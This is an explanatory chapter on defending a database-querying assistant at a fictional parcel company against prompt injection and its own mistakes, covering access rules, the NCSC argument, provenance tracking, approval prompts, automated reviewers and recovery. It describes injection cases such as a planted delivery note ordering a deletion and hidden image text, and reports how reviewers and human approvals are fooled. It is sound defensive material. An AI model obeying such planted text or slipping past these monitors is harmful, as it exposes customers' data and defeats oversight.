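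Newer studies have tested whether a model can enforce detailed access rules itself. *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control* (Fei and Yang, 2026) added user roles to three collections of database questions. A sales analyst, for example, might be allowed to see sales data but not employees' personal details. The prompt stated which operations the role could perform on which columns, and the model had to write a permitted query or refuse.

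| Model | Violations, Spider | Violations, BIRD | Violations, LiveSQLBench |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 2.6% | 10.5% | 17.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 4.9% | 7.7% | 13.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 10.9% | 21.2% | 35.3% |
| Qwen2.5 14B | 36.9% | 56.2% | 59.4% |

The models date from 2025 or earlier, and newer ones may do better. Violations became more common as the databases and questions became more complicated, even though nobody was trying to trick the models. Not every violation would have exposed forbidden data, because the count includes cases where a model should have refused but wrote a different query using only permitted columns.

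Fei and Yang also tried leaving forbidden columns out of the database description. This reduced violations for several models but raised GPT-5-mini's violations on BIRD from 12.7% to 26.8%. The model more often guessed the names of hidden columns, and more often answered questions it should have refused. Fine-tuning an open model on examples of the rules cut its violations on Spider from about 50% to 6%, but the model went from never refusing legitimate requests to doing so in 20% of all cases.

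*When the Application Layer Is Disposable* (2026) reports a similar result for rules about which data a database may hold. Models wrote more checks when the prompt stated the rules, but those checks were not reliably correct. For one rule, the average query grew from 16 words to 153, which gave the model more opportunities to make a mistake.

*Beyond Document Retrieval* (2026) identifies where authorisation happens as the most important design choice for agents that query company data. If the model that writes the queries also decides what a user may see, any change to the prompt could weaken security. A developer who rewords Tern's template to make the answers friendlier would have to retest the access rules. If a database policy controls access instead, the prompt's wording does not affect which rows the customer can reach.

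### Warnings in tool descriptions

A developer may have to use someone else's MCP server that lacks proper checks. In *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions*, Shi, Fu and colleagues (2026) tried to make such servers safer without changing their code. They rewrote the tool descriptions that the model receives, specifying which arguments could be dangerous and what kinds of request to refuse. They also had the model review each call before the application ran it.

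They tested GPT-4o with 792 malicious prompts based on known vulnerabilities:

| Description the model received | Successful attacks without a review | Successful attacks with a review |
|---|---|---|
| Original | 63.9% | 3.2% |
| General warning | 28.4% | 1.5% |
| Warning about the wrong vulnerability | 12.8% | 0.5% |
| Warning about the right vulnerability | 9.1% | 0.13% |

The lowest figure is a single success in 792. These are large improvements for little work, and most tools could make them, since only 7% of the 1,856 tool descriptions Shi and colleagues collected contained any security guidance. Repairing the code is slower. The repairs they examined changed an average of 204 lines, and four of 41 left the flaw exploitable.

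Warning the model about the wrong vulnerability worked almost as well as warning it about the right one, so much of the benefit probably came from making the model more cautious in general. The benchmark contains only malicious prompts, so it does not measure how many legitimate requests a more cautious model would refuse. The tests covered only GPT-4o.

This defence still depends on the model to detect dangerous calls, and it cannot detect the danger in an ordinary-looking request to delete shipment 1045. A better tool description could make Tern's assistant more careful, but `delete_shipment` would still need its ownership check.

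### What an assistant can still do under strict limits

The available evidence suggests that strict limits usually do little to reduce a language model's ability to handle requests that the developer did not foresee, which is why people choose language models. When Ma and colleagues ran 123 working database servers under MAP's ceilings, the servers' legitimate operations continued to work. The checks added 28 microseconds to the average query, although a server could handle 13.6% fewer queries in a given time.

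Miyamoto, Xin and Yamana (2026), in *Policy-Conditioned Constrained Decoding for Column-Level Access Control in Text-to-SQL*, show that a strict limit can even let an assistant answer more. A model writes a query one token (a word or part of a word) at a time. Their system tracks the query's structure as the model writes it and removes forbidden column names from the choices for the next token. The rules depend on how the query uses a column, so an employee's salary might be available in an average but not on its own.

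The results for one open model, Qwen 2.5 Coder 32B, on 1,034 questions were:

| Method | Queries that broke the rules | Permitted queries that ran |
|---|---|---|
| Rules in the prompt | 4.8% | 25.8% |
| Rules in the prompt, then a second check by the same model | 1.4% | 18.3% |
| Forbidden columns removed during writing | 0% | 80.6% |

When the rules were only in the prompt, the model refused most questions, including many it could have answered. It often found a permitted query instead when it could not use the forbidden columns. A smaller Qwen model reached 88.7%, also without breaking the rules.

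However, a permitted query can still be incorrect. On questions with a known permitted answer, the larger model returned the right result only 48.2% of the time. The method also supports only basic SQL and requires control over how the model chooses each token, which providers of hosted models rarely allow.

Tern's customers would lose very little, because they need to find, change and cancel their own shipments, and fixed functions can cover all of this. "Clear my delivered shipments" could become a function that takes no arguments from the model. The developer would write the conditions on the customer and the status once, and the model could not omit either. The manager who wants to know which streets had the most failed deliveries can still have an assistant that writes its own SQL, provided it uses a read-only role and a parser that permits counting and sorting.

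Telling the model the rules is useful even when the database enforces them. Fei and Yang point out that if the database rejects a query, the data is safe but the user has no answer. A model that knows the rules can write a permitted query the first time or explain what it cannot provide. In their tests, GPT-5 wrongly refused only 0.7% to 4.5% of requests.

Row-level security can also make an answer misleading, because it removes rows without raising an error. If customer 17 asks how many parcels Tern delivered last week, the database will count only hers, and the assistant may present the number as the company's total. When a request goes partly beyond the user's rights, *Beyond Document Retrieval* recommends that the agent reject it, ask the user to narrow it, or explain which part it has answered.

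Permitted queries can also reveal private information when combined. Suppose Tern lets its depot managers see drivers' average pay but not individual salaries. If four drivers earn £30,000 on average, and the average rises to £31,000 when a fifth joins, the fifth must earn £35,000. Each query would pass every check described here. Wang and colleagues warn that ordinary database access controls may miss leaks that build up in this way. Preventing them requires limiting what a series of answers can reveal, for example by refusing averages for very small groups and tracking what each user has already asked.

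## Can instructions be separated from data?

Checks on queries and tool calls limit the damage a model can do when it follows instructions in a delivery note, but they do not stop it from following them. Databases once had a similar weakness, which parameterised queries fixed by keeping commands separate from values. If a prompt could separate instructions from data just as strictly, Tern's model would never treat text in a stranger's note as an instruction.

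### The comparison with SQL injection

In December 2025 the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) published an argument that language models have no such repair. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, reasons roughly as follows:

1. SQL injection happens when a database executes part of somebody's data as a command.
2. A database handles commands and data differently. It carries out commands, and it stores or compares data. An application can therefore send the two separately, and the database will never execute a value that arrives as data, whatever the value contains.
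3. A language model handles everything in the same way. It receives the whole prompt as one sequence of tokens and predicts the next token from the ones before it.
4. Nothing inside the model therefore corresponds to a parameterised query. A developer can mark some text as data, train the model to give it less weight or scan it for attacks, but the model may still act on it.

David C, the NCSC's technical director for platforms research, concludes that there is "a good chance" nobody will ever properly fix prompt injection in the way that parameterised queries fixed SQL injection. His claim is about guaranteed prevention, so it would still be true if attacks on a particular model almost always failed.

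The history of SQL injection supports the second step. David C writes that these attacks peaked around 2010 and are now rare on websites, after a decade of breaches led to better defaults. The advisories that Shifat and colleagues collected show that some developers still don't use the fix, but those who do no longer have to worry about how cleverly an attacker words a value.

The third step needs a qualification, because the model does receive information about where each passage came from. Companies that run chat models put special markers into the prompt to show where the developer's instructions, the user's message and each tool result begin, and they can prevent outsiders from inserting genuine markers. However, the markers are part of the same sequence as everything else, and the model treats the passages differently only because of its training. Tern's database, by contrast, needs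 no training to treat 1042 as data when it receives it as the value of `$1`.

A database can store or compare a delivery note without understanding it, but Tern uses a language model so that the note's meaning can affect the answer. Many ordinary notes are also instructions. "Ring twice, bell is faint" tells the driver what to do, and a useful assistant has to pass it on. Filtering every instruction out of the notes would make the column useless, so the model has to work out whom each instruction is for.

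David C therefore suggests treating a language model as an "inherently confusable deputy". Capabilities could fix Hardy's confused compiler, but he argues that a language model will always remain confusable to some degree. He advises developers to assume that an attacker might gain direct use of every tool the model can call, and to limit those tools with ordinary code. If a system cannot tolerate the remaining risk, he says, it may be a poor use for a language model.

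He also passes on a rule from a discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista. While a model is processing text from someone, it should have no more privileges than that person. Under this rule, Tern's staff assistant could not delete shipments or read other customers' addresses while a stranger's note was in its prompt, because the stranger cannot do those things. Losing access to the addresses would make it awkward to summarize the day's shipments.

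In its 2026 list, OWASP similarly recommends designing the surrounding system on the assumption that the model's instruction boundary will eventually fail, according to Infosecurity Magazine.

### Training models to rank instructions by source

One reply to the NCSC's argument is that a model can learn the distinction even if its architecture does not enforce it. OpenAI and other companies train models to rank instructions by source. The developer's instructions outrank the user's, and text that a tool returns has no authority of its own. Training rewards the model for obeying the higher-ranking source when a lower-ranking one contradicts it. Tern's model receives delivery notes as tool results, so if it had learned the ranking perfectly, it would not carry out a command planted in a note.

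Companies now automate much of this training. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) describes a model the company trained to attack its other models, because human testers could not find weaknesses fast enough. GPT-Red learned through self-play, in which a system improves by competing repeatedly against an opponent, and OpenAI uses its attacks to make new models more resistant. The company says its latest models had already reached the top of the commonly used robustness tests, so those tests could no longer measure progress.

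OpenAI reports direct and indirect attacks separately. Three of its 2026 models have published results. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* covers GPT-5.6 Sol, ctsd's *GPT-6 Astra* (2026), from a German IT company, covers GPT-6 Astra, and Cross (2026), in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, covers GPT-6 Sol:

| Model | Direct attacks that succeeded | Indirect attacks that succeeded | Reported by |
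|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | About 0.05% | 3.77% | TechRepublic |
| GPT-6 Astra | 0.01% | 8.5% | ctsd |
| GPT-6 Sol | 0.01% | 2.87% | Cross |

Direct attacks very rarely succeeded, but indirect attacks succeeded at least 75 times as often on every model, and Tern's delivery notes are an indirect route. One likely reason is that the model can refuse a user's suspicious message but has to read a tool's result closely to do its job. The tests may have differed between models, so the table does not show that GPT-6 Astra is the weakest of the three. TechRepublic cautions that such percentages describe attempts in a company's test environments, not the probability of a breach in a live product.

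Anthropic's results are the best evidence for training. According to The Decoder, no attack succeeded against Claude Opus 5 in 129 test scenarios in which the model operated a browser. In a more general test by Gray Swan, a security company, attackers given 15 attempts succeeded 2.0% of the time against Opus 5, down from 5.5% against the earlier Opus 4.8. Two other Anthropic models, Mythos 5 and Fable 5, had rates of 2.6% and 2.8%.

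Claude Opus 5.5 followed in September. According to Anthropic's *System Card* (2026), it matched or beat Opus 5 on every prompt injection test the company reports, but in some situations it is more likely than earlier models to follow malicious instructions.

Even a result of zero depends on the test. By the rule of thumb for tests with no failures, 129 scenarios without a successful attack are compatible with a true success rate of up to about 2.3%. ctsd reports that 4.8% of indirect attacks succeeded against the same Opus 5, so three sources of test scenarios produced three different rates for one model.

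Google's models are harder to compare with others. According to VentureBeat, the company's system card for Gemini 3 gives no absolute attack success rates. Gray Swan did test Gemini 3 Pro, and The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports rates as high as 92% for a group of models that included Gemini 3 Pro and OpenAI's GPT-5.1. Both models date from 2025, so the figure is a poor guide to what either company offers now.

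Training has clearly made attacks harder, more so than the NCSC's fourth step might suggest. But unlike a parameterised query, it does not separate instructions from data reliably in every setting. VentureBeat describes tests in which Claude Opus 4.6 resisted all 200 attack attempts in a restricted coding environment. When the model worked through a graphical interface with extended reasoning turned on, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time.

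### Why a low success rate can still be too high

Suppose that a planted delivery note has a 3% chance of making Tern's staff assistant do what its author wants, which is close to GPT-6 Sol's rate for indirect attacks. A stranger books 50 parcels and writes a slightly different note for each. If *p* is the chance that one attempt succeeds and *n* is the number of attempts, the chance that at least one succeeds is:

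```
1 − (1 − p)^n  =  1 − 0.97^50  =  0.78
```

The stranger has a 78% chance of success with 50 notes and a 95% chance with 100. These figures assume that every note has the same 3% chance of success, regardless of whether the others succeed.

The Decoder's figures for Claude Opus 4.5 make it possible to check this assumption:

| Attempts | Predicted if independent | Measured by Gray Swan |
|---|---|---|
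| 1 | 4.7% | 4.7% |
| 10 | 38% | 33.6% |
| 100 | 99% | 63% |

The formula is fairly accurate for ten attempts but greatly overstates the danger at 100, probably because some scenarios are much easier to attack than others. If half of the test scenarios could never be broken and each attempt on the rest had a 9.4% chance, the average for one attempt would still be 4.7%, but the success rate would reach only 31% after ten attempts and could never exceed 50%. The success rate against Opus 4.6 levels off in the same way in the graphical test. From its 17.8% rate for one attempt, the formula predicts near-certain success within 200 attempts, but VentureBeat reports 78.6%, or 57.1% with additional safeguards.

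This is little reassurance for Tern, because 63% is still far too high for a system that holds customers' addresses. Real attackers may also do better than the formula, since they can learn from failed attempts. Published defences have often failed against attackers who adapt to them.

The number of attempts matters as much as the success rate, and a company has some control over how many an attacker gets. David C recommends logging the model's inputs, outputs and tool calls, because an attacker will probably have to refine an attack and will cause failed calls in the process. If one new account starts making dozens of bookings, each with a long and strange note, the company should notice early. He warns against relying on lists of forbidden phrases, because an attack can always be reworded. Marking outside text as data, for example with tags, can make attacks harder.

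A better-trained model is worth having for the same reason. If the chance of success per attempt fell from 3% to 0.01%, the rate that OpenAI reports for direct attacks, the chance that at least one of 50 independent attempts succeeded would be about 0.5%. But an attacker who could automate 10,000 attempts would have a 63% chance. With a parameterised query, the chance that a value becomes a command is zero however many times the attacker tries.

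### One model to plan and another to read

The NCSC's argument rules out a reliable boundary within a single prompt, but an application can also separate instructions from data outside the model, by calling it more than once and deciding what each call receives. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes six designs based on the principle that an agent that has read untrusted text must be unable to take any consequential action because of it.

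The central design, which Willison proposed in 2023, uses two models. A **privileged model** plans the work and can request tool calls, but never reads untrusted text. A **quarantined model** reads the untrusted text but has no tools. An ordinary program, the orchestrator, passes values between them.

Suppose a clerk at Tern asks the staff assistant to send the driver of shipment 1045 the phone number in its delivery note. The work would go like this:

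1. The privileged model receives the clerk's request and a list of tools. It has not seen the note, so it refers to the note's contents by name:

```python
note  = get_delivery_note(1045)
phone = ask_reader("Find the phone number.", note)
message_driver(1045, phone)
```

2. The orchestrator runs the first line and stores the text under the name `note`. It does not show the text to the privileged model.
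3. The orchestrator gives the text to the quarantined model with the instruction to find a phone number. The quarantined model replies with some text.
4. The orchestrator checks that the reply has the form of a phone number and stores it as `phone`.
5. The orchestrator sends the value of `phone` to the driver.

Now suppose the note also contains a planted order to delete shipment 1042. The quarantined model may follow the order and reply with a request for the deletion. The reply is not a phone number, so the orchestrator rejects it. Even without that check, the driver would only receive a strange message, because the plan contains no deletion and the order never reached the privileged model. A more persuasive note would not get the shipment deleted either.

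The other designs separate the plan from the data to different degrees. Applied to Tern, they would work like this:

| Design | What the application does | What a planted note can still affect |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from fixed functions and never sees their results | Nothing the model does |
| Plan, then execute | The agent commits to a list of tool calls before it reads any notes | The arguments of those calls, and the answer |
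| Map-reduce | A separate model call reads each note and returns, say, yes or no, and code combines the results | The result for its own parcel |
| Two models | The planner handles values by name, and the reader has no tools | The value that the reader returns |
| Code, then execute | The planner writes a whole program, which may include calls to a reader | The values that pass through the program |
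| Context minimisation | The application deletes the customer's message before the model words the answer | As before, since this design is aimed at the customer's message |

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that an assistant that queries a database should plan its actions before executing them. This would have prevented route three, in which a clerk's request for a summary led to a deletion. The agent would have committed to one `SELECT` before it read the planted note, and could not have added a `DELETE` afterwards.

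The chains in Pedro and colleagues' prompt-to-SQL study roughly followed this design. Planted text could make them give false answers but not change a record. That is consistent with the limits of planning before execution, although the study was not a test of the design.

For a customer service chatbot, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest combining an action selector with context minimisation. They illustrate context minimisation with a car dealer's chatbot. A customer asks for a quote and adds text meant to make the model offer a huge discount. The application turns the request into a database query and then deletes the customer's message, so the model that writes the reply receives the real prices but not the demand for a discount. Tern could do the same when a customer asks about a parcel and tries to make the assistant promise a refund.

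All six designs give up some flexibility. An action selector can take only the actions its developer listed. An agent that must plan in advance cannot change its plan when it reads something unexpected, even if the change would be sensible. A clerk could not ask such an agent to "deal with whatever the delivery notes ask for", because the plan would depend on the notes. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues accept this limitation. They think a fully general agent is unlikely to offer reliable guarantees while it depends on current language models, and that developers should ask what kinds of restricted agent are still useful.

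### CaMeL and the origin of each value

Keeping the plan fixed does not protect the values that go into it. Suppose the clerk asks the assistant to email a customer's invoice to the address in the delivery note. The plan is to read the note, extract the email address and send the invoice there. If a stranger wrote the note, they can put their own address in it and receive the invoice without giving the model any instructions.

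*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), by Debenedetti and colleagues at Google and ETH Zurich, addresses this problem with a system called CaMeL. The privileged model writes its plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. A special interpreter runs the program and records where each value came from and who may see it. When the program combines two values, the result inherits the restrictions of both. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks these records against the developer's policies.

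At Tern, a policy might allow the assistant to send an invoice only to an address from the customer's account. The interpreter would have a record that the address in the clerk's task came from a delivery note, so it would block the email. The model isn't involved in this decision, so nothing in the note can influence it. The check resembles taint analysis, except that it follows the values while the program runs.

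Debenedetti and colleagues tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a set of tasks in simulated email, banking, travel and chat software, with attacks planted in the data. CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks with its security guarantee in force, compared with 84% for an agent without the defence. That loss, about one in twelve of the tasks the undefended agent could do, is modest for protection that does not depend on the attacker's wording, but a company that handles mainly open-ended requests would probably lose more.

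The guarantee also covers only the data flows that the policies forbid. If Tern's developer forgets to write a policy for invoices, CaMeL will run a program that sends invoices to a stranger.

Other systems apply the same idea to existing agents. They track provenance (where data came from) and block sensitive tool calls that depend on untrusted sources. *Agentic AI Defense* (Yocam, Vaidyan and colleagues, 2026) discusses several of them alongside CaMeL. SafeFlow carries labels from one step of an agent's work to the next, and ProvenanceGuard intercepts tool calls as they happen. NeuroTaint, however, only examines records of completed work, so it can explain a theft but not prevent it.

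Yocam and colleagues found a gap in this approach. Existing systems attach the label when a tool returns text, but an attacker can hide an instruction in a normal-looking image with no visible text, such as the logo in an email signature. One of the agent's tools later decodes the hidden text, and one agent passes it to another as an ordinary intermediate result, with nothing to show that an outsider wrote it.

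The defence sits in the layer between the agents and their tools. This layer labels text as untrusted when a tool decodes it, and gives the same label to any result with at least one untrusted input. It signs each label with a secret key, so an agent that an attacker has taken over cannot forge or alter one. It also keeps its own record of which untrusted text has entered each agent's context. Before a sensitive call, such as sending email or exporting passwords, the layer checks this record instead of relying on what the agent reports.

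The researchers tested 24 attacks, using three ways of hiding text in an image:

| Defence | Attacks that leaked data |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Scanner that looks for suspicious keywords | 62.5% |
| Parser that looks for suspicious patterns | 62.5% |
| Labels from the moment of decoding | 0% |

Twenty-four attacks would be too few to show that a detector has a low failure rate. The small number matters less for this defence, which never judges what the text means, so attackers gain nothing by rewording it. Its protection depends on every tool call passing through the trusted layer. An ordinary label-tracking system also stopped the attacks when all the agents were trustworthy, but it failed when a label had to pass through an agent the attacker controlled.

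Under the strict rule, agents at first completed only 67% of legitimate tasks, because some of those tasks depend on decoded text. If Tern's staff photograph a damaged label and have a tool read the shipment number, the rule marks that number as untrusted and blocks any sensitive action based on it. Yocam and colleagues added a procedure for declaring specific text trustworthy and recording each decision. Completion then rose to 100%, and the attacks still failed. An attacker would now most like to influence this procedure, so its safety depends on who or what makes the decisions.

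These systems provide much of the separation between instructions and data that the NCSC argues a model cannot provide. The planner's program works like the fixed SQL command, and the untrusted text passes through it as a value. The NCSC's argument still applies to the model itself, since the quarantined model is as easy to mislead as before. Natanzi and Tang describe vulnerabilities in language model systems as failures of information flow, provenance, privilege and state, which would make the application the natural place to fix them.

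### What a separated design does not cover

A delivery note can cause harm even if it contains no instructions. Suppose the note for shipment 1045 contains a false statement that the customer has moved, along with a new address. When a clerk asks where the parcel should go, the quarantined model correctly reports the address in the note. If the driver uses that address, the parcel goes to a thief, even though no instruction from the note entered the plan.

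Beurer-Kellner and colleagues acknowledge this limit in their examples. When an assistant emails a manager the day's schedule, planted text in the calendar cannot change the recipient, but it can change the schedule. When separate model calls sort files into invoices and other documents, a malicious file can still be classified as an invoice. The accounts department then has to deal with a fake invoice, although the model has not made matters worse, since the attacker could have submitted one directly.

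Provenance can help if the application uses it. Tern could forbid address changes that come from a delivery note, or show the clerk which parts of an answer a stranger wrote. But knowing where a note came from doesn't show whether it is true. The false documents in Wang and colleagues' tests would also have been a problem for CaMeL whenever the user had asked the agent to rely on them.

The designs also trust the person who makes the request. When customer 17 asks for shipment 1045 to be deleted, the privileged model plans the deletion because it is supposed to follow her instructions. Only an ownership check stops it. A well-meaning user can cause similar trouble by copying text from a malicious website into the chat, because the planner treats that text as part of the request. Context minimisation keeps the text away from the final answer, but by then it has already influenced the choice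 of action.

Even if the plan is sound, the answer can leak data when it reaches the clerk's browser, for example through an image address. The principle behind the six designs covers this case by requiring that a restricted agent's output cannot leak data through links, but the developer still has to build that protection at the browser.

Separation also does not correct a planner's own mistakes. If the privileged model leaves a condition out of a `DELETE` statement, as in route two, the plan contains no untrusted text, and the interpreter will run it as written.

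## Confirmation, reversible deletion and recovery

A harmful action can pass every check described so far. For example, customer 17 asks to clear only her delivered shipments, but the query deletes all her shipments, including the parcel in transit. Somebody has to stop such a query just before it runs or undo its effects afterwards.

An application can undo a deletion but not a leak. *Can You Undo It?* (Waghmare and Sufi, 2026) gives three requirements for restoring exactly what existed before an agent acted. Somebody must have recorded the earlier state in full, whoever restores it must already have the authority to write it back, and no outsider can have seen, received or acted on the changed state. Tern can meet the first two for a shipment record. Once a stranger reads a leaked address, the third cannot be met, and a backup does not help. Tern can replace a leaked password, but customer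 23's address would stay exposed unless the customer moved.

### What a request for approval should show

Consider the query from route two, which would delete every delivered shipment instead of only customer 17's. If the model wrote the request for approval, it might ask, "Clear customer 17's delivered shipments?" A clerk would probably agree, because the question describes what the customer wanted, not what the query does. A useful request looks more like this:

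```
Delete 4 shipments and their 12 tracking events?

  1041   customer 17   delivered
  1043   customer 17   delivered
  1044   customer 23   delivered
  1046   customer 31   delivered

Customer 17 asked: "Clear my delivered shipments."
```

Showing the operation, the number of rows and their owners makes the mistake easy to see. The application can build the list by running a `SELECT` with the same conditions as the model's query. After approval, it should delete exactly the listed shipments, because other rows may have started to match in the meantime. Tern should show this request to a clerk, not to customer 17, who has no right to see other customers' rows.

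The application has to supply the confirmation text because the model may fail to detect an error in its own query. An attacker could also plant instructions in a delivery note for the model to describe a deletion as something harmless.

Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested how much the content of a request matters. In one scenario, a user allows an agent to send an auditor summary totals only. Planted text makes the agent copy raw invoice rows into a file, and the agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The recipient and the tool are both permitted, so the request looks normal. Eighty volunteers each judged 12 requests, half of them unsafe, using one of four designs:

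| What the reviewer saw | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| Also the user's original restriction and a log of every step | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
| The same facts, arranged to show the combined effect | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

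The last design showed facts from a recorder of the agent's actual calls, not from the agent's own account. Most of the improvement came from showing more facts. Arranging them better may have helped further, but the statistical interval for that difference includes zero. Even with the best design, people approved about one unsafe request in four, although judging requests was their only task. A reviewer at work, who might see one dangerous request among hundreds, would probably do worse.

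### Approval fatigue

People who receive many approval requests stop reading them, a problem known as approval fatigue. The requests are also often unhelpful. According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), most approval prompts in live products show a raw command on a single line.

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users of the coding agent approve 97% of its permission prompts. Most of the commands in those prompts are probably safe, so the approval rate alone doesn't prove that people are careless. Anthropic therefore commissioned an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through each tester's session, the experimenters replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more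 prompts.

Anthropic's automatic classifier blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). The testers refused only six that the classifier would have allowed, so using both would have raised the total to 89.6%. Anthropic published these figures to support making automatic review the default, and the testers were not working on their own projects, where they would have had more to lose. Still, smaller studies also found that people often don't read prompts. In *Options, Not Clicks* (2026), only 3 of 16 participants said they read them carefully, and 13 used "Always Allow" just to dismiss them. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports of agents harming files, and in 80 of them users had let the agent's actions run without approval.

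Users of Claude Code reject 39% of the plans it proposes. Some may simply prefer another approach, but the rate suggests that people think harder about larger, rarer decisions. Tern should therefore ask for confirmation only before consequential actions, such as permanently deleting data or sending customers' data outside the company. Waghmare and Sufi similarly suggest that an agent should act and then notify the user if the action can be fully undone, but ask first if it can't. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, recommends that permission prompts show how recoverable an action is.

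### Automated review

In automated review, a second model decides whether an agent's action may go ahead. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) describes the version in OpenAI's Codex and illustrates its use inside the company with 10,000 actions. Of these, 9,280 stayed within the agent's sandbox and needed no approval. The reviewer approved 713 of the other 720 and refused seven. After four of the refusals the agent found a safer way to continue, and after the other three it stopped and asked the user.

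The reviewing model takes the user's request into account, so it might detect that customer 17 never mentioned other people's shipments. In OpenAI's tests, it refused 90.3% of overeager actions, a category that includes irreversible operations. It refused 99.3% of actions caused by prompt injection in three categories of attack, but the rate was 90.2% when the test also included destructive deletions and data tampering. Trębacz and colleagues say that many of the additional misses were not serious. They also report that testers misled the model into approving commands, and they don't expect systems of this kind to provide firm guarantees.

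Anthropic's classifier works similarly, and the agent goes back to asking the user for approval after the classifier refuses three actions in a row or 20 in a session. Anthropic still advises users to review the agent's actions themselves for high-stakes changes to live infrastructure. Automated review is a better default than approval by a tired person, but a system that misses one dangerous action in ten also needs a way to undo the damage.

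### Soft deletion and a delay

Tern can make most mistaken deletions harmless by keeping the row. Soft deletion means marking a record as deleted while keeping it, so that someone can restore it. The table needs one more column:

```sql
ALTER TABLE shipments ADD COLUMN deleted_at timestamptz;
```

The `delete_shipment` function then fills in that column instead of removing the row:

```python
def delete_shipment(shipment_id, session):
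    result = database.execute(
        "UPDATE shipments SET deleted_at = now() "
        "WHERE id = %s AND customer_id = %s AND deleted_at IS NULL",
        (shipment_id, session.customer_id))
    if result.rowcount != 1:
        raise LookupError("No such shipment on this account")
```

If customer 17 removes shipment 1042 by mistake, an employee can restore it with one command:

```sql
UPDATE shipments SET deleted_at = NULL WHERE id = 1042;
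```

The shipment's tracking events also remain, because `ON DELETE CASCADE` applies only when the database actually removes a row. Depots can keep scanning the parcel in the meantime. However, every ordinary query must now exclude the marked rows, and if a developer forgets this condition, customers will see shipments they have deleted.

A scheduled job removes the marked rows for good after a delay:

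```sql
DELETE FROM shipments
WHERE deleted_at < now() - interval '14 days';
```

The job should use a database role that the assistant cannot use, and the assistant's own role should lose its `DELETE` privilege. The function also has to set `deleted_at` itself. If the model could choose the value, it could enter an old date, and the job would remove the row that night.

The delay must be long enough for someone to notice the mistake. Kaya, Bozoğlan and Gündoğdu (2026), in *When an AI agent makes a mistake in a database*, gave small open models tasks with hidden hazards on nine database systems, including Cassandra and ClickHouse. Cassandra takes a snapshot before it drops or empties a table. With its default settings, agents destroyed protected data in 62 of 432 trials, and the researchers could restore it every time. ClickHouse keeps a dropped table for eight minutes by default. That was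 enough in the experiment, where recovery began within seconds, but it would not help a company that noticed the mistake the next morning.

Soft deletion does not protect a value that the model overwrites. If the assistant replaces the address on shipment 1042, the old address is gone unless Tern also keeps a history of changes.

### Cancelling a query that changes too many rows

A transaction is a group of commands that the database applies completely or not at all. Until the application commits the transaction, it can roll it back, which cancels everything in it. The application can therefore run a query, see how many rows it changed and then decide whether to keep the result:

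```python
def run_with_limit(query, expected):
    with database.transaction():   # any error rolls it back
        result = database.execute(query)
        if result.rowcount > expected:
            raise RuntimeError("More rows than expected")
```

Before running the model's query for "clear my delivered shipments", Tern's application counts the rows that should match:

```sql
SELECT count(*) FROM shipments
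WHERE customer_id = 17 AND status = 'delivered';   -- returns 2
```

The model's query, which lacks the condition on the customer, deletes four shipments. This exceeds the limit of two, so the function raises an error and the database cancels the deletion. All six shipments and 18 tracking events remain. The limit would also stop the query that keeps the condition on the customer but omits the one on status, because it deletes three shipments.

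The developer's code has to supply the expected number, since the model could repeat its mistake when counting. But a developer who can write this count in advance could also write the deletion as a fixed function, which is simpler and safer. For unforeseen requests, Tern can set only a general limit, such as ten rows per request. This would stop a query from emptying a large table but not from deleting four shipments. No row limit can detect a query that deletes shipment 1045 instead of 1042, because each is one row.

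Rolling back works only before the commit, and database systems differ in which commands a rollback can undo. In Kaya and colleagues' tests, PostgreSQL restored a table that a script had dropped inside an open transaction. MySQL and MariaDB commit automatically before dropping a table, so the rollback did not restore it. The application should reject any model output with more than one command, because a `COMMIT` written by the model would end the transaction early.

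Transactions are poorly suited to tasks that last for hours or wait for a person's approval. *BranchBench* (2026) explains that databases optimise them for short pieces of work. The agent can instead work on a branch, a separate version of the data that someone can later merge into the live version. In *Git4Data*, Gou, Zhang and colleagues (2026) built a system that supports branches and can compare two versions. Such a comparison would be useful in a request for approval because it shows what the agent actually changed.

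### Backups and the recovery point

Kaya and colleagues tested recovery from scripted mistakes, with no model involved, on PostgreSQL, MySQL, MariaDB and SQLite. Without any preparation, PostgreSQL permanently lost protected rows after 17 of 21 mistakes, and the other three did about as badly. With the minimum backup that each system's documentation describes, none of the four lost any. This confirms that the instructions work, but it doesn't show that a company would lose nothing, because the researchers made each backup just before the mistake.

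A backup protects against an agent's mistakes only if the agent cannot delete it. In the experiments with models, agents caused permanent losses in 392 trials under default settings. In 215 of these, the only thing they destroyed was a backup copy stored in the same database as the original. Many were following instructions, because one task told them to remove everything not on a list, and the list omitted the backup. PocketOS's agent also deleted backups when it deleted the live data. Tern should keep its backups in a separate account, with credentials that neither the assistant nor the main application holds.

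The recovery point is the latest moment to which a company can return its data. Suppose Tern backs up its data at 02:00 every night, and the assistant deletes the wrong shipments at 14:00. With only the backup, the recovery point is 02:00. If Tern records 50 new shipments an hour, restoring the backup would lose 12 hours of records, covering 600 shipments.

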